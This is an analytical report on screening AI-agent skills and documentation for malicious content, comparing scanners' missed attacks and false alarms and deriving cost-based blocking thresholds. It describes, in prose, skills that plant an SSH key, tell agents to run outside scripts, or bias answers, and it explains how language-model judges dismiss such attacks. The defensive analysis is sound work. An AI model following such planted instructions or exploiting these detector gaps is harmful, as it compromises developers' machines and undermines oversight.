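While looking up the weather, the skill `evilweather` adds a stranger's SSH key to the file that lists who may log in to the machine. Skill-scanner has no rule for this, but SkillSpector does, so skill-scanner's developers could presumably write one too. In documentation, the new rule would also match server setup guides that tell readers to add their own key to the same file. Matching only complete keys would reduce these false positives, since most guides print a placeholder.

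More precise rules can't solve every case. *SkillsMetric* (2026) found that static analysis works well on attacks that leave structural traces, such as suspicious combinations of imported modules, but fails when normal-looking code serves an abnormal purpose. A rule broad enough to catch that code would also flag similar code in legitimate skills.

The second cause covers requests such as ClawHavoc's false prerequisites, which contain no command for a rule to match. A rule that looked for "download" and "run" in the same paragraph would flag a large share of all installation guides. In the OASB dataset, where the attacks are in ordinary language, skill-scanner's rules caught 7 of 93 malicious skills, and adding a language model, Qwen3.6, raised this to 90. Judging by the F1 scores, the scanner flagged none of the 68 benign skills with or without the model. However, OASB is synthetic, and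 its attacks may be easier to tell from harmless text than real attacks are.

### What would happen if PSV-001 blocked skills

Raising a finding's severity could address the third cause, but it can also produce many false positives. PSV-001, skillscan-security's medium-severity rule for undeclared network access, fires on 48.3% of malicious skills and 29.3% of benign ones.

If PSV-001 did block skills, it could catch at most the 27 malicious skills that this detector graded too low, which would raise recall from 85.1% to 88.4%. The rule also fires on about 173 of the 591 benign skills. The detector already blocks half of the benign skills, and the study doesn't report how many of the 173 are among them. If half are, the change would block about 87 more benign skills and raise the false-positive rate from 50% to 65%.

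The tradeoff looks worse at a realistic base rate. Among 10,000 skills, 1% of them malicious, the same change would catch about three more attacks and block about 1,450 more legitimate skills. The tradeoff would probably be even worse for documentation. A chunk doesn't declare permissions, so the rule might fire on any example that contacts a server.

### Attacks found but not blocked

Detectors that use a language model differ in that, for most of the attacks they miss, some part of the detector had already found the attack. The table leaves out labelling errors.

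| Detector | Attack not found | Found but graded too low | Found but dismissed or filtered out | Share of misses after the attack was found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | 66 | 119 | 0 | 64.3% |
| SkillSpector | 134 | 203 | 109 | 70.0% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 47 | 28 | 324 | 88.2% |
| skill-vetter | 16 | 0 | 151 | 90.4% |

SkillSpector's rules alone would have blocked 109 skills that passed after the model reviewed the findings. Most of these cases occurred with Qwen3.6. Skipping the review would restore the detections but also bring back false alarms. With Qwen3.6, recall would rise by at most 12 percentage points and the false-positive rate by at least 10.

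skill-vetter dismissed 92 attacks because the skill contained no executable code, and AI-Infra-Guard dismissed 90 for much the same reason. The skills told the reader to run an outside script, for example, or described a harmful action without supplying a program for it. This is a poor reason to dismiss an attack, because a coding agent can carry out written instructions itself. It would be especially damaging in a documentation screener, where missing code is normal.

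Missing code also caused false alarms by skill-vetter, and 107 of the findings behind them concerned code that was absent or that it couldn't inspect. The judge therefore counted missing code against some harmless skills and in favour of some malicious ones. Telling it to draw no conclusion from missing code should reduce both kinds of error.

Other dismissals are harder to fix without extra false alarms. skill-vetter detected that `project-init` downloads and runs unverified code and recommended removing or verifying that step, but approved the skill with the step still in it. The study found 19 such conditional approvals. Blocking these skills until someone repairs them would stop the attacks, but it would also delay legitimate skills with similar flaws.

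AI-Infra-Guard missed 120 attacks because it classified them as outside its scope. One was `financial-analysis`, which contains instructions for the agent to bias its valuations of companies. The detector classified this as a compliance problem. A wider scope would catch it, but detectors already raise many false alarms by treating exaggerated descriptions and a lack of risk warnings as signs of malice.

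In 39 of the 66 cases where skill-scanner missed the attack, the model never received the skill's instructions because they exceeded an input limit and the scanner left them out. The scanner could instead split long files and examine every part. This would use more tokens and give the model more text to flag by mistake, but the scanner wouldn't have to judge any passage more strictly. A documentation service would mainly face this problem if it screened whole pages, since chunks are short.

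### Results by attack type

Guo and colleagues sorted the malicious skills in their benchmark by whether the attack is in the code, in the instructions, or dependent on both, for example when the instructions prepare a file that a script then uses.

| Detector | Recall, code | Recall, instructions | Recall, both | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentry's scanner, with model | 99.8% | 97.6% | 99.8% | 23.4% |
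| AI-Infra-Guard | 99.2% | 74.8% | 99.1% | 15.5% |
| skill-scanner, with model | 96.5% | 83.1% | 98.9% | 36.6% |
| skill-scanner, rules only | 46.9% | 18.7% | 72.0% | 9.6% |

Attacks in the instructions are the hardest to detect, which is a problem for documentation services because they handle mostly text. Sentry's scanner still caught 97.6% of them, so the paper's results don't support the claim in its abstract that even the strongest detector collapses on these attacks.

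Instructions to insert biased or false content into the agent's answers were the hardest to detect. AI-Infra-Guard caught 35.8% of these attacks and skill-scanner with a model caught 32.1%. This fits the dismissal of `financial-analysis` and suggests that the detectors' definition of an attack is often too narrow to include dishonest advice. A documentation service would have to decide whether to block text that secretly steers developers towards one vendor's product.

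Results on real attacks differ considerably from those on the full benchmark because the real sample has little variety. Of the 703 malicious skills the researchers collected from public sources, 609 deliver malware, and two accounts published 81% of the total. VirusTotal caught 99.3% of the malware-delivery skills but only 3 of the 33 that steal credentials. Its recall was 87.9% on the real skills and 21.6% on the full benchmark.

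Near-identical copies of one skill can also distort a detector's score. In the study by Yang, Ying and colleagues, AI-Infra-Guard with DeepSeek-V4 caught only 9 of the 95 malicious skills in MalWild, although it caught 80% across all seven datasets. Guo and colleagues report that 86 of MalWild's original 157 skills came from one upload and are nearly identical. Repeating the same wrong judgement on each copy could account for most of the misses.

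Other benchmarks add little detail. *SkillSecurer* (2026) has only 20 injection cases in each of nine categories. skill-scanner's confirmed misses were concentrated in credential exposure and indirect injection, where it found 15 of the 20 cases in each. SkillSpector missed one case of script execution. These counts are for individual injections, and the researchers were comparing the scanners with their own.

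SkillTrustBench also has nine threat categories. Tencent Zhuque Lab's *Who is the strongest gatekeeper for Agents?* (2026) raises the question of which types of attack are easiest for scanners to miss, but the *SkillTrustBench Leaderboard* publishes only overall scores.

A detector's recall can also differ between categories because different people wrote the attacks. *MaliciousSkillBench* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) combines skills from 11 sources, but one of them, SkillTrustBench, supplied 2,755 of the 3,320 skills labelled as running or delivering code. Recall in that category would mostly show how well a detector handles SkillTrustBench's style.

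### Moving a threshold and adding information

Many of the remedies above reduce either missed threats or false positives by increasing the other. If a detector gives each item a fixed score, moving its threshold can never raise recall while lowering the false-positive rate. But new information can reduce both errors if it raises the scores of malicious items and lowers those of benign ones.

Combining two tools doesn't necessarily add useful information. Guo and colleagues also paired the package scanners and injection defences they had tried on skills. Flagging a skill when either tool reports a problem works like lowering the threshold. With OSSGadget and NeMo Guardrails, this caught 99.2% of malicious skills but flagged 96.4% of benign ones. Flagging a skill only when both tools report a problem works like raising the threshold. With MalGuard and Llama Guard 3, this removed nearly all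 the false alarms but caught only 5.0% of malicious skills.

A combination works better if the tools have different strengths and one of them rarely raises false alarms. VirusTotal flagged only 4 of the 4,000 benign skills, so adding its flags to AI-Infra-Guard's would cause at most four more false alarms. On the 703 real malicious skills, the published figures imply that recall would rise from 74% to at least 93%. Guo and colleagues didn't test this pair, and their choice of benign skills favours VirusTotal. A documentation service would also have to download whatever a chunk recommends, because VirusTotal is better at recognizing malware than the text that leads to it.

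Added information can also make a weak rule useful. Suppose a detector could check whether each network request that triggers PSV-001 goes to the service named in the skill's description. In an invented example, this check clears 90% of the benign skills that match the rule and mistakenly clears 20% of the malicious ones. Blocking the remaining matches would catch 38.6% of all malicious skills and flag 2.9% of benign ones. If 1% of skills were malicious, about 12% of the blocked skills would be malicious, compared with 1.6% for the rule alone. Blocking these matches would still add some false alarms to those from other rules, so the detector could reduce the total only by also using the check to clear existing findings.

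In some tests, language models have both missed fewer threats and raised fewer false alarms than text patterns. In *AgentTrap* (2026), text patterns caught 31 of 91 malicious skills and flagged 7 of 50 benign ones, while a language model that read the same files caught 80 and flagged 2. The sample is small, but the improvement in recall is too large to be chance.

Choosing a better model can also reduce false alarms without an obvious loss of recall. *Securing the AI Agent* (2026) reports that the models tested with AI-Infra-Guard on SkillTrustBench differ most in their false-positive rates, and that the best have recall near 100%. DeepSeek V4 Flash missed one of 390 risky skills and flagged 11 of 166 normal ones, while GPT-5.5 also had high recall but flagged 31 normal skills. Tencent makes both the scanner and the benchmark. The leaderboard also counts a "suspicious" verdict as a detection,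 so these results look better than results based on blocking decisions.

In tests by Truong-Le and colleagues, the models doing the judging missed more attacks when they were also given static findings without results from a trial run, perhaps because they treated a lack of serious findings as evidence of safety.

Learned detectors can also misclassify unfamiliar material as malicious. Wang and colleagues trained a simple classifier on word frequencies in skills. It flagged 9.4% of benign skills when the training and test sets came from the same sources. It flagged 62.4% of benign skills from sources absent from its training data, with a recall of 95.6%. Documentation differs from skills more than one collection of skills differs from another, so a service that screens documentation with a classifier trained on skills should expect many false alarms until it retrains the classifier on documentation.

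### The revised skill-vetter prompts

Yang, Ying and colleagues made two additions to skill-vetter's prompt to reduce both errors. The first addresses four bad reasons for dismissing an attack that the judge has already identified: that the skill contains no executable code, that the problem concerns only the quality of an answer, that the harm comes later, and that someone could still remove the harmful part. The second lists seven kinds of content that don't justify rejection by themselves, including ordinary authentication, commanding language and code the judge can't inspect.

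The researchers tested the new prompt on 150 malicious and 150 benign held-out skills from each of MalSkillBench and SkillTrustBench. They also tested it on 154 malicious and 112 benign skills from SkillSafetyBench, which they had not used when studying the errors. The counts are averages over three runs.

| Dataset | Model | Missed, old prompt | Missed, new prompt | Benign flagged, old prompt | Benign flagged, new prompt | F1, old prompt | F1, new prompt |
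|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| MalSkillBench | Qwen3.6 | 22.7 | 19.7 | 12.7 | 7.7 | 0.878 | 0.905 |
| MalSkillBench | GPT-5.4 | 10.7 | 6.3 | 66.3 | 8.7 | 0.784 | 0.950 |
| MalSkillBench | DeepSeek-V4 | 20.3 | 14.3 | 19.3 | 5.0 | 0.867 | 0.933 |
| SkillTrustBench | Qwen3.6 | 8.7 | 7.3 | 5.7 | 2.7 | 0.952 | 0.966 |
| SkillTrustBench | GPT-5.4 | 1.3 | 2.0 | 53.0 | 15.0 | 0.846 | 0.946 |
| SkillTrustBench | DeepSeek-V4 | 5.7 | 6.3 | 5.7 | 2.3 | 0.962 | 0.971 |
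| SkillSafetyBench | Qwen3.6 | 109.3 | 114.3 | 1.7 | 0.7 | 0.445 | 0.402 |
| SkillSafetyBench | GPT-5.4 | 52.3 | 32.3 | 7.7 | 1.7 | 0.772 | 0.877 |
| SkillSafetyBench | DeepSeek-V4 | 103.0 | 65.3 | 0.3 | 0.3 | 0.496 | 0.723 |

F1 rose in eight of the nine settings, and false positives fell or stayed the same in all of them. Missed threats and false positives both fell in five settings, so reducing one doesn't always require increasing the other. The new prompt adds instructions for interpreting the facts the judge already has about a skill, but no new facts.

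Misses rose in three settings. The two increases on SkillTrustBench are less than one skill on average, which is within the variation between runs. The increase with Qwen3.6 on SkillSafetyBench is also uncertain, but the judge still missed about three-quarters of the attacks there.

SkillSafetyBench is the fairest of the three tests because the other held-out skills come from the same collections as the ones the researchers studied, and so may contain similar attacks. Even with GPT-5.4, which gave the best result on SkillSafetyBench, the screening missed 21% of the malicious skills. The researchers tested the two additions only together, so the effect of each is unknown.

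A documentation service couldn't safely adopt the new prompt unchanged. The prompt instructs the judge to treat installing packages a task needs from trusted repositories such as npm or PyPI as harmless, and not to reject a skill for unverified dependencies alone. This prevents many false alarms about ordinary installation commands, but the judge could approve misspelled or abandoned package names, so the service would still need to look up each package separately.

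## What a false positive costs and where to set the threshold

Every detector that catches most attacks also flags some harmless material, so a documentation service has to decide how many good passages it will lose to stop one more attack. That number depends on how much damage each kind of error does and on how much of the content is harmful.

### What an agent loses

When a screener removes a good passage, the agent usually still writes the code, relying on what its model learned in training, which is often out of date. Schmid and McDonald (2026), in *Closing the knowledge gap with agent skills*, tested Gemini models on 117 prompts asking for code that uses Google's Gemini API. An answer failed if it used one of Google's old software development kits. Gemini 3.1 Pro passed 28% of the prompts by itself, and two 3.0 models passed 6.8%. According to The Decoder's *Google's new Gemini API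 Agent Skill patches the knowledge gap*, Gemini 3.1 Pro passed 96.6% with a skill that described the current kits and linked to the official documentation.

In *AGENTS.md outperforms skills in our agent evals*, Vercel, the company behind Next.js, reports testing an agent on features too new to be in its training data. The pass rate was 53% without documentation and 100% with an index in the project's `AGENTS.md` file that pointed to the relevant pages. When Vercel supplied the documentation as a skill instead, the agent never opened it in 56% of cases, and the pass rate stayed at 53%. A false positive that removes a passage does no harm if the agent would not have read the passage anyway.

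Next.js' *AI Agent Evaluations* tests 12 models on 21 tasks each. On average, the models completed 64% of the tasks without the bundled documentation and 88% with it. The 88% apparently combines the tasks completed without documentation and those completed only with it, so it may not account for tasks where documentation made the result worse.

In *An Empirical Study of Automating Agent Evaluation*, Zhou, Woo and colleagues (2026) built a system that writes code for evaluating other AI agents, and tested it with and without access to Context7. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, the code ran and gave meaningful results on the first try 65% of the time with Context7 and 20% without it. The rate was lower without Context7 because the code named models in a form that the libraries didn't accept. This gap probably exaggerates the value of documentation, because a version with neither Context7 nor the system's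 other built-in guidance succeeded 30% of the time. The guidance may have steered the agent towards a library that it couldn't use properly without documentation.

| Task | Model | Success without documentation | Success with documentation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini API code | Gemini 3.1 Pro | 28% | 97% |
| Next.js code | GPT-5.4 | 86% | 95% |
| Next.js code | Claude Opus 4.6 | 71% | 100% |
| Next.js code | Kimi K2.5 | 19% | 52% |
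| Agent evaluation code | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 20% | 65% |
| Agent evaluation code | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 47.5% | 62.5% |

A typical false positive should do much less harm than these gaps suggest, because each test removed all the documentation, whereas a screener usually removes one passage. Google and Vercel also tested material about their own products and focused on recent changes. All the models date from March 2026 or earlier. Newer ones may have some of these features in their training data, though the libraries will have changed again since.

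A single passage can still matter a lot if it contains the only working example. *When LLMs Meet API Documentation* (2025) found that retrieved documentation raised average pass rates by 83% to 220% on four less common Python libraries. *BIM Information Extraction Through LLM-based Adaptive Exploration* (2026), which summarizes what is apparently the same study, reports that removing the code examples lowered accuracy from 0.66–0.82 to 0.22–0.39. Detectors often flag code examples, such as the Base64 text behind most of SkillGate's false alarms, so a false positive may remove the most helpful part of a page.

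When a screener drops the right page, the next-best match that replaces it can also do harm, and the agent has no way of knowing that a better page existed. In *When LLMs Meet API Documentation*, models sometimes used the wrong function because a page about an irrelevant one ranked too high. Even an agent that knows about a change to a library may not be able to use it without the documentation. In *When LLMs Lag Behind* (2026), adding the library's documentation to a description of the change raised the share of answers that adopted the change by 24% and the share that ran by 57%.

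Working without documentation also uses more tokens. In *Improve coding agents’ performance with Gemini API Docs MCP and Agent Skills*, Nguyen (2026) reports that Google's documentation server and skill together cut tokens per correct answer by 63%, so a model prompted without them used about 2.7 times as many.

A false positive could make the developer less safe. An agent that can't find the installation page may remember an old version with a known vulnerability, or make up a package name, as a language model did with `react-codeshift`. Nobody seems to have measured how often this happens.

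### Costs to maintainers, reviewers and users

When a classifier wrongly rejects a library's pages, users end up with broken code and the maintainers may lose users. Context7's ranking could add to that loss. According to Shannon, Context7 generates questions that developers might ask about a library, scores how well the stored documentation answers them, and favours high-scoring libraries over similar ones. If the classifier rejects the page about logging in, the remaining documentation may answer login questions badly, and the library may drop in the ranking. The published score could alert the maintainers to a problem, but it wouldn't show whether the classifier had rejected the page or nobody had written it.

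Other filters make similar mistakes more visibly. Some web firewalls reject any request containing a path such as `/etc/passwd`, which attackers often try to read, so a writer who tries to save a Linux tutorial that mentions it may get an error message. Antivirus software may quarantine a security researcher's attack samples and show an alert. A maintainer whose page is missing from a documentation service may get no notice.

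Reviewers lose time to false positives, and the amount depends on how many items a detector flags. MalGuard, the package scanner, flagged only about four new Python packages a day, which one person could easily check. Most of the skill detectors would flag more.

Users may respond to frequent warnings by ignoring them. Anyone who followed SkillSpector's advice would have to give up almost half the skills on ClawHub. Yang, Fu and colleagues argue that mistaken blocks erode developers' trust, but they didn't study users. If a scanner catches 94% of attacks and users heed half of its warnings, the warnings stop only 47% of attacks. A scanner that catches 77% would protect users better if they always heeded its warnings.

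### How many flags are correct

Precision, the share of flagged items that are harmful, depends on recall (r), the false-positive rate (f) and the base rate (b). Out of all screened items, a share rb are harmful and flagged, and a share f(1 − b) are harmless and flagged. Therefore:

precision = rb / (rb + f(1 − b))

In 1999, Stefan Axelsson applied this reasoning to intrusion detection, the automatic search for attacks in records of computer activity. He argued that attacks are so rare among ordinary events that the false-alarm rate limits such a system more than its ability to recognize attacks does.

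The table shows what SkillGate's flags would be worth at different base rates if its recall (76.9%) and false-positive rate (1.13%) stayed the same.

| Share of skills that are malicious | Where the share comes from | Precision | Harmless skills flagged per malicious skill caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| 20% | Article about ClawHub | 94% | 0.06 |
| 9.1% | SkillsBench test set | 87% | 0.15 |
| 0.16% | 157 of 98,380 public skills | 10% | 9 |
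| 0.10% | 95 of the same 98,380 | 6% | 15 |

The 20% figure is doubtful. Yang, Fu and colleagues took it from a LinkedIn article that counted 1,184 malicious skills on ClawHub in February 2026. Koi Security counted more than 10,700 skills there mid-month, and 1,184 would be about 11% of those.

The two lowest shares come from the study behind the MalWild dataset, one from before Yang, Ying and colleagues reviewed its labels and one from after. That study may also have missed some attacks, so the true share could be higher than either figure.

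Low base rates would create a lot of work for reviewers. On the 98,380 skills, SkillGate would catch about 121 of the 157 malicious ones and flag about 1,110 harmless ones. If each review took five minutes, checking every flagged skill would take about 100 hours. Without the judge, SkillGate's patterns would flag about 26,600 harmless skills, which would take more than 2,200 hours to review, over a year of full-time work.

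Nobody seems to have published a base rate for harmful documentation. It is probably lower than for skills, especially per chunk, because even a hostile library may contain only a few harmful chunks among many copied from a legitimate project. If one chunk in 10,000 were harmful and SkillGate's error rates applied to chunks, it would flag about 147 harmless chunks for each harmful one it caught, a precision of 0.7%.

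The formula also makes detectors quick to compare, because a flag multiplies the odds that an item is malicious by r/f, whatever the base rate. This factor is about 68 for SkillGate, about 15 for skill-vetter with Qwen3.6, 3.3 for SkillGate's patterns alone, and 1.8 for ClawVet. The comparison is rough because the figures come from different test sets. Still, a ClawVet flag doesn't even double the odds, so it can't justify much action if malicious skills are rare.

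### Errors across a library

A false-positive rate that sounds tiny for one chunk can affect most libraries. Suppose a screener wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless chunks, and a clean library has 2,000 of them. If the errors are independent, the chance of at least one false flag is:

1 − (1 − 0.001)^2000 ≈ 86%

Keeping that chance below 5% would require a false-positive rate of about one in 39,000 chunks. No study of skills or documentation has shown a rate nearly that low, and confirming it would take far more than 39,000 harmless chunks.

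The false positives are probably correlated. If the same login example appears on 40 pages, a detector that flags one copy will probably flag the others. Fewer libraries would then have false flags, but each one affected would lose more chunks. The average would still be two lost chunks per library.

Losing two chunks out of 2,000 may be tolerable, but a fixed number of flags is a poor reason to reject a whole library. If one flag were enough, the service would reject 86% of clean libraries of this size. Requiring five flags would reduce that to about 5%, again assuming independent errors, but would reject about 96% of clean libraries as large as Next.js, which has 9,372 snippets. It would also accept a hostile library with four harmful chunks.

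### When blocking is worthwhile

Let p be the probability that an item is harmful, given everything the service knows about it. Let C_FP be the cost of blocking a harmless item and C_FN the cost of letting a harmful one through. Blocking has an expected cost of (1 − p) × C_FP, because it does damage only if the item is harmless. Allowing the item has an expected cost of p × C_FN. Blocking is therefore cheaper when:

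p × C_FN > (1 − p) × C_FP

Solving for p gives the threshold:

p > C_FP / (C_FP + C_FN)

If a false positive is as bad as a miss, the service should block anything that is more likely harmful than not. If a miss is 99 times as bad, it should block anything with more than a 1% chance of being harmful.

Nobody has measured these losses for documentation, but an invented example shows how to estimate them. Suppose losing a passage makes one task in ten fail, and each failure takes the developer 20 minutes to fix, for an average loss of two minutes per lookup. Suppose a harmful passage leads to stolen credentials in one lookup in ten, and each theft takes 60 hours to deal with, for an average loss of six hours per lookup. A miss then loses 180 times as much time as a false positive, so the threshold for blocking a passage is a 1/181 probability that it is harmful, or about 0.55%.

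The number of readers doesn't affect this calculation, because blocking a harmless page and missing an attack both hurt more developers, in the same proportion, when the page is popular. In practice, people may notice an attack on a popular page sooner, which limits the damage, whereas a silent false positive can last for months.

Under these assumptions, a SkillGate flag would justify blocking at a base rate of 157 in 98,380, because its 10% precision is far above the 0.55% threshold. A match with SkillGate's patterns alone would give a probability of 0.53%, just below the threshold. For chunks, SkillGate's flags would barely exceed the threshold at a base rate of one in 10,000 (0.7%) and fall far below it at one in 100,000 (0.07%). At the lower rate, the service would need further evidence, such as a package lookup, before blocking anything.

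A judge's confidence score is not the same as p, the probability that the content is malicious. If SkillGate's default blocking threshold of 0.7 were a true probability, it would make sense only if a false positive did more than twice as much harm as a miss, and the researchers believe misses are worse. A service could estimate the probability for each confidence level by checking how much of a sample of its own content at that level is malicious. The result would depend on the base rate of attacks in that content, so scores calibrated on a test set full of attacks would be too high for a service where attacks are rarer.

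### Whether SkillGate's judge is worth its misses

On the 1,650 skills in SkillsBench, SkillGate's judge removes 389 false positives but causes SkillGate to miss 20 more malicious skills. Using the patterns without the judge is therefore better only if one miss does more harm than about 20 false positives.

Yang, Fu and colleagues call the judge's tradeoff "strongly favorable", but they also treat recall as the main measure because a miss does more harm than a wrongly blocked skill. Both views can be right only if a miss is between one and about 20 times as harmful as a false positive. The researchers don't estimate this ratio, and 20 seems low for an attack that can steal cloud credentials.

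The case for the judge is much stronger at realistic base rates, because there are more harmless skills for every malicious one:

| Share of skills that are malicious | False positives the judge prevents for each extra miss |
|---|---|
| 20% | 8 |
| 9.1% | 20 |
| 0.16% | about 1,200 |
| 0.10% | about 2,000 |

At the invented cost ratio of 180, a hub should use the patterns alone in the first two cases and add the judge in the last two. A service that uses a test set with a high share of malicious items can therefore choose the wrong detector, even if it measures recall and the false-positive rate perfectly.

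The same method can help choose a confidence threshold. Lowering SkillGate's threshold from 0.70 to 0.14 would catch about eight more malicious skills on the benchmark and add about three false positives. If 157 in 98,380 skills are malicious, that means about 23 more false positives for each additional attack caught. The lower threshold is better if a miss is 180 times as bad as a false positive and the threshold works equally well on skills outside the benchmark.

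### Grading the response by severity

A screener can flag a document without blocking it. Yang, Fu and colleagues sorted the false alarms on SkillsBench's 1,500 benign skills by severity and counted how many skills each detector would block if only HIGH and CRITICAL findings led to a block.

| Detector | Critical | High | Medium | Low | Total | Would block |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ClawVet | 39 | 257 | 307 | 153 | 756 | 296 |
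| skill-scanner, MEDIUM threshold | 9 | 10 | 242 | 0 | 261 | 19 |
| SkillGate | 3 | 0 | 13 | 1 | 17 | 3 |
| skill-scanner with model | 11 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 11 | 11 |

This policy would help ClawVet the least of the first three, still blocking 296 harmless skills, almost one in five. Only 3 of SkillGate's 17 false alarms would lead to a block. The false alarms from skill-scanner with a model are all critical because the researchers counted only critical findings for that version.

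The table doesn't show how many attacks the policy would let through. The researchers compare SkillGate's 3 wrongful blocks with its recall of 76.9%, but that recall includes detections of any severity. They don't report how many of the roughly 115 malicious skills that SkillGate caught had high or critical findings. That number could be much lower, since skill-scanner's static rules lose most of their correct detections when only findings rated HIGH or above are counted.

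The researchers estimate that users would notice only about three blocks if SkillGate quarantined medium-severity findings. But SkillGate aborts an `npx skills add` installation for a quarantine as well as for a block, so users would also notice the 13 quarantined skills. Quarantine is less disruptive than a block only if someone reviews the skill soon.

### Choosing between a block and a review

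The cost model can include human review. Let C_R be the cost of one review, and assume for now that the reviewer is always right and works immediately. Reviewing is cheaper than allowing the item if p × C_FN > C_R, and cheaper than blocking it if (1 − p) × C_FP > C_R. The service should therefore review an item when:

C_R / C_FN < p < 1 − C_R / C_FP

Suppose the loss is 1 for a false positive, 180 for a miss, and 0.1 for a review. Review is then the best choice when the probability that an item is malicious is between about 0.06% and 90%. At a base rate of 157 malicious items in 98,380, a SkillGate flag is right 10% of the time, so the flagged item would go to a reviewer. At a base rate of 20%, the flag is right 94% of the time, so the item would be blocked automatically.

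The number of readers matters when deciding whether to review a flagged page, because the service only has to review the page once, but a wrong decision affects everyone who needs it. A flagged page in a popular library is usually worth reviewing. For a library that hardly anyone looks up, automatic blocking may make more sense.

Real reviewers also make mistakes, as did the participants who overlooked the planted instructions in Kao and colleagues' README test. A reviewer who sees the detector's finding should do better, but someone who has just dismissed 100 false alarms may dismiss a real attack too.

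Unlike newly published skills, documentation often has an earlier version to fall back on. If a refresh adds a suspicious command to a page, the service can keep serving the old text while someone reviews the new text. Developers then get slightly outdated instructions instead of none. This won't help with a new library, or if the update fixes a security problem in the old text.

### Blocking chunks or whole libraries

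Blocking only one chunk limits the damage from a false positive, but it can leave an agent with only part of a procedure. In one of Vercel's tests, an agent wrote the correct code for a new caching feature but left out the required change to a configuration file. That agent had access to the documentation but used it badly. Blocking the chunk about the configuration file could cause even a careful agent to make the same mistake.

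A confirmed attack in one chunk is much stronger evidence about the other chunks than a false alarm is. If a reviewer confirms that a library's owner deliberately planted a command to steal credentials, the rest of that library is suspect, including chunks that no detector flagged. The service should then block the library and check the owner's other libraries. If an outsider added the command to a legitimate project, restoring the previous version would do less damage than blocking the library.

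Warnings are less useful for documentation than for skills. ClawHub can show a warning to a person before installation, but a documentation service sends its replies to a model. If a flagged passage contains a prompt injection, the model has already read it by the time it can act on the warning. A warning makes more sense for a command with an uncertain target, because the agent could ask the developer for confirmation before running it. Many developers let their agents work without confirmation, so some warnings would have no effect.

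The service could also withhold the passage and say so in its reply. The agent could then tell the developer that the answer is incomplete, instead of guessing from old training data. But the agent may fetch the missing page directly from the web, without screening. The notice should therefore ask the agent to get the developer's approval first, although the service can't enforce this.

### Correcting mistakes

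A false positive also does more harm the longer it lasts. If each day without a page does the same damage, correcting the mistake after one day instead of 90 divides C_FP by 90. This lowers the threshold, C_FP / (C_FP + C_FN), so a service that corrects its mistakes quickly can block more pages.

Context7 continually reviews flagged content, but doesn't explain whether a review can restore a chunk. In December 2025, Upstash invited users to report libraries with missing or fraudulent content. Each report created a GitHub issue, and staff reviewed these issues almost daily. A maintainer could report a wrongly rejected page this way, but would first have to notice that it was missing.

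Notifying the owner of a claimed library whenever the classifier rejects a chunk would solve that problem. The notice could name the page and the general reason, such as "installation command from an unknown domain", so that an honest maintainer could explain or rewrite the command.

Attackers can claim libraries too, and detailed notices would help them adjust their text until it passed. They could also appeal repeatedly, since a language-model judge often gives different verdicts on the same borderline case. An appeal should therefore add new evidence, such as a package lookup or a human review, instead of rerunning the same judge.
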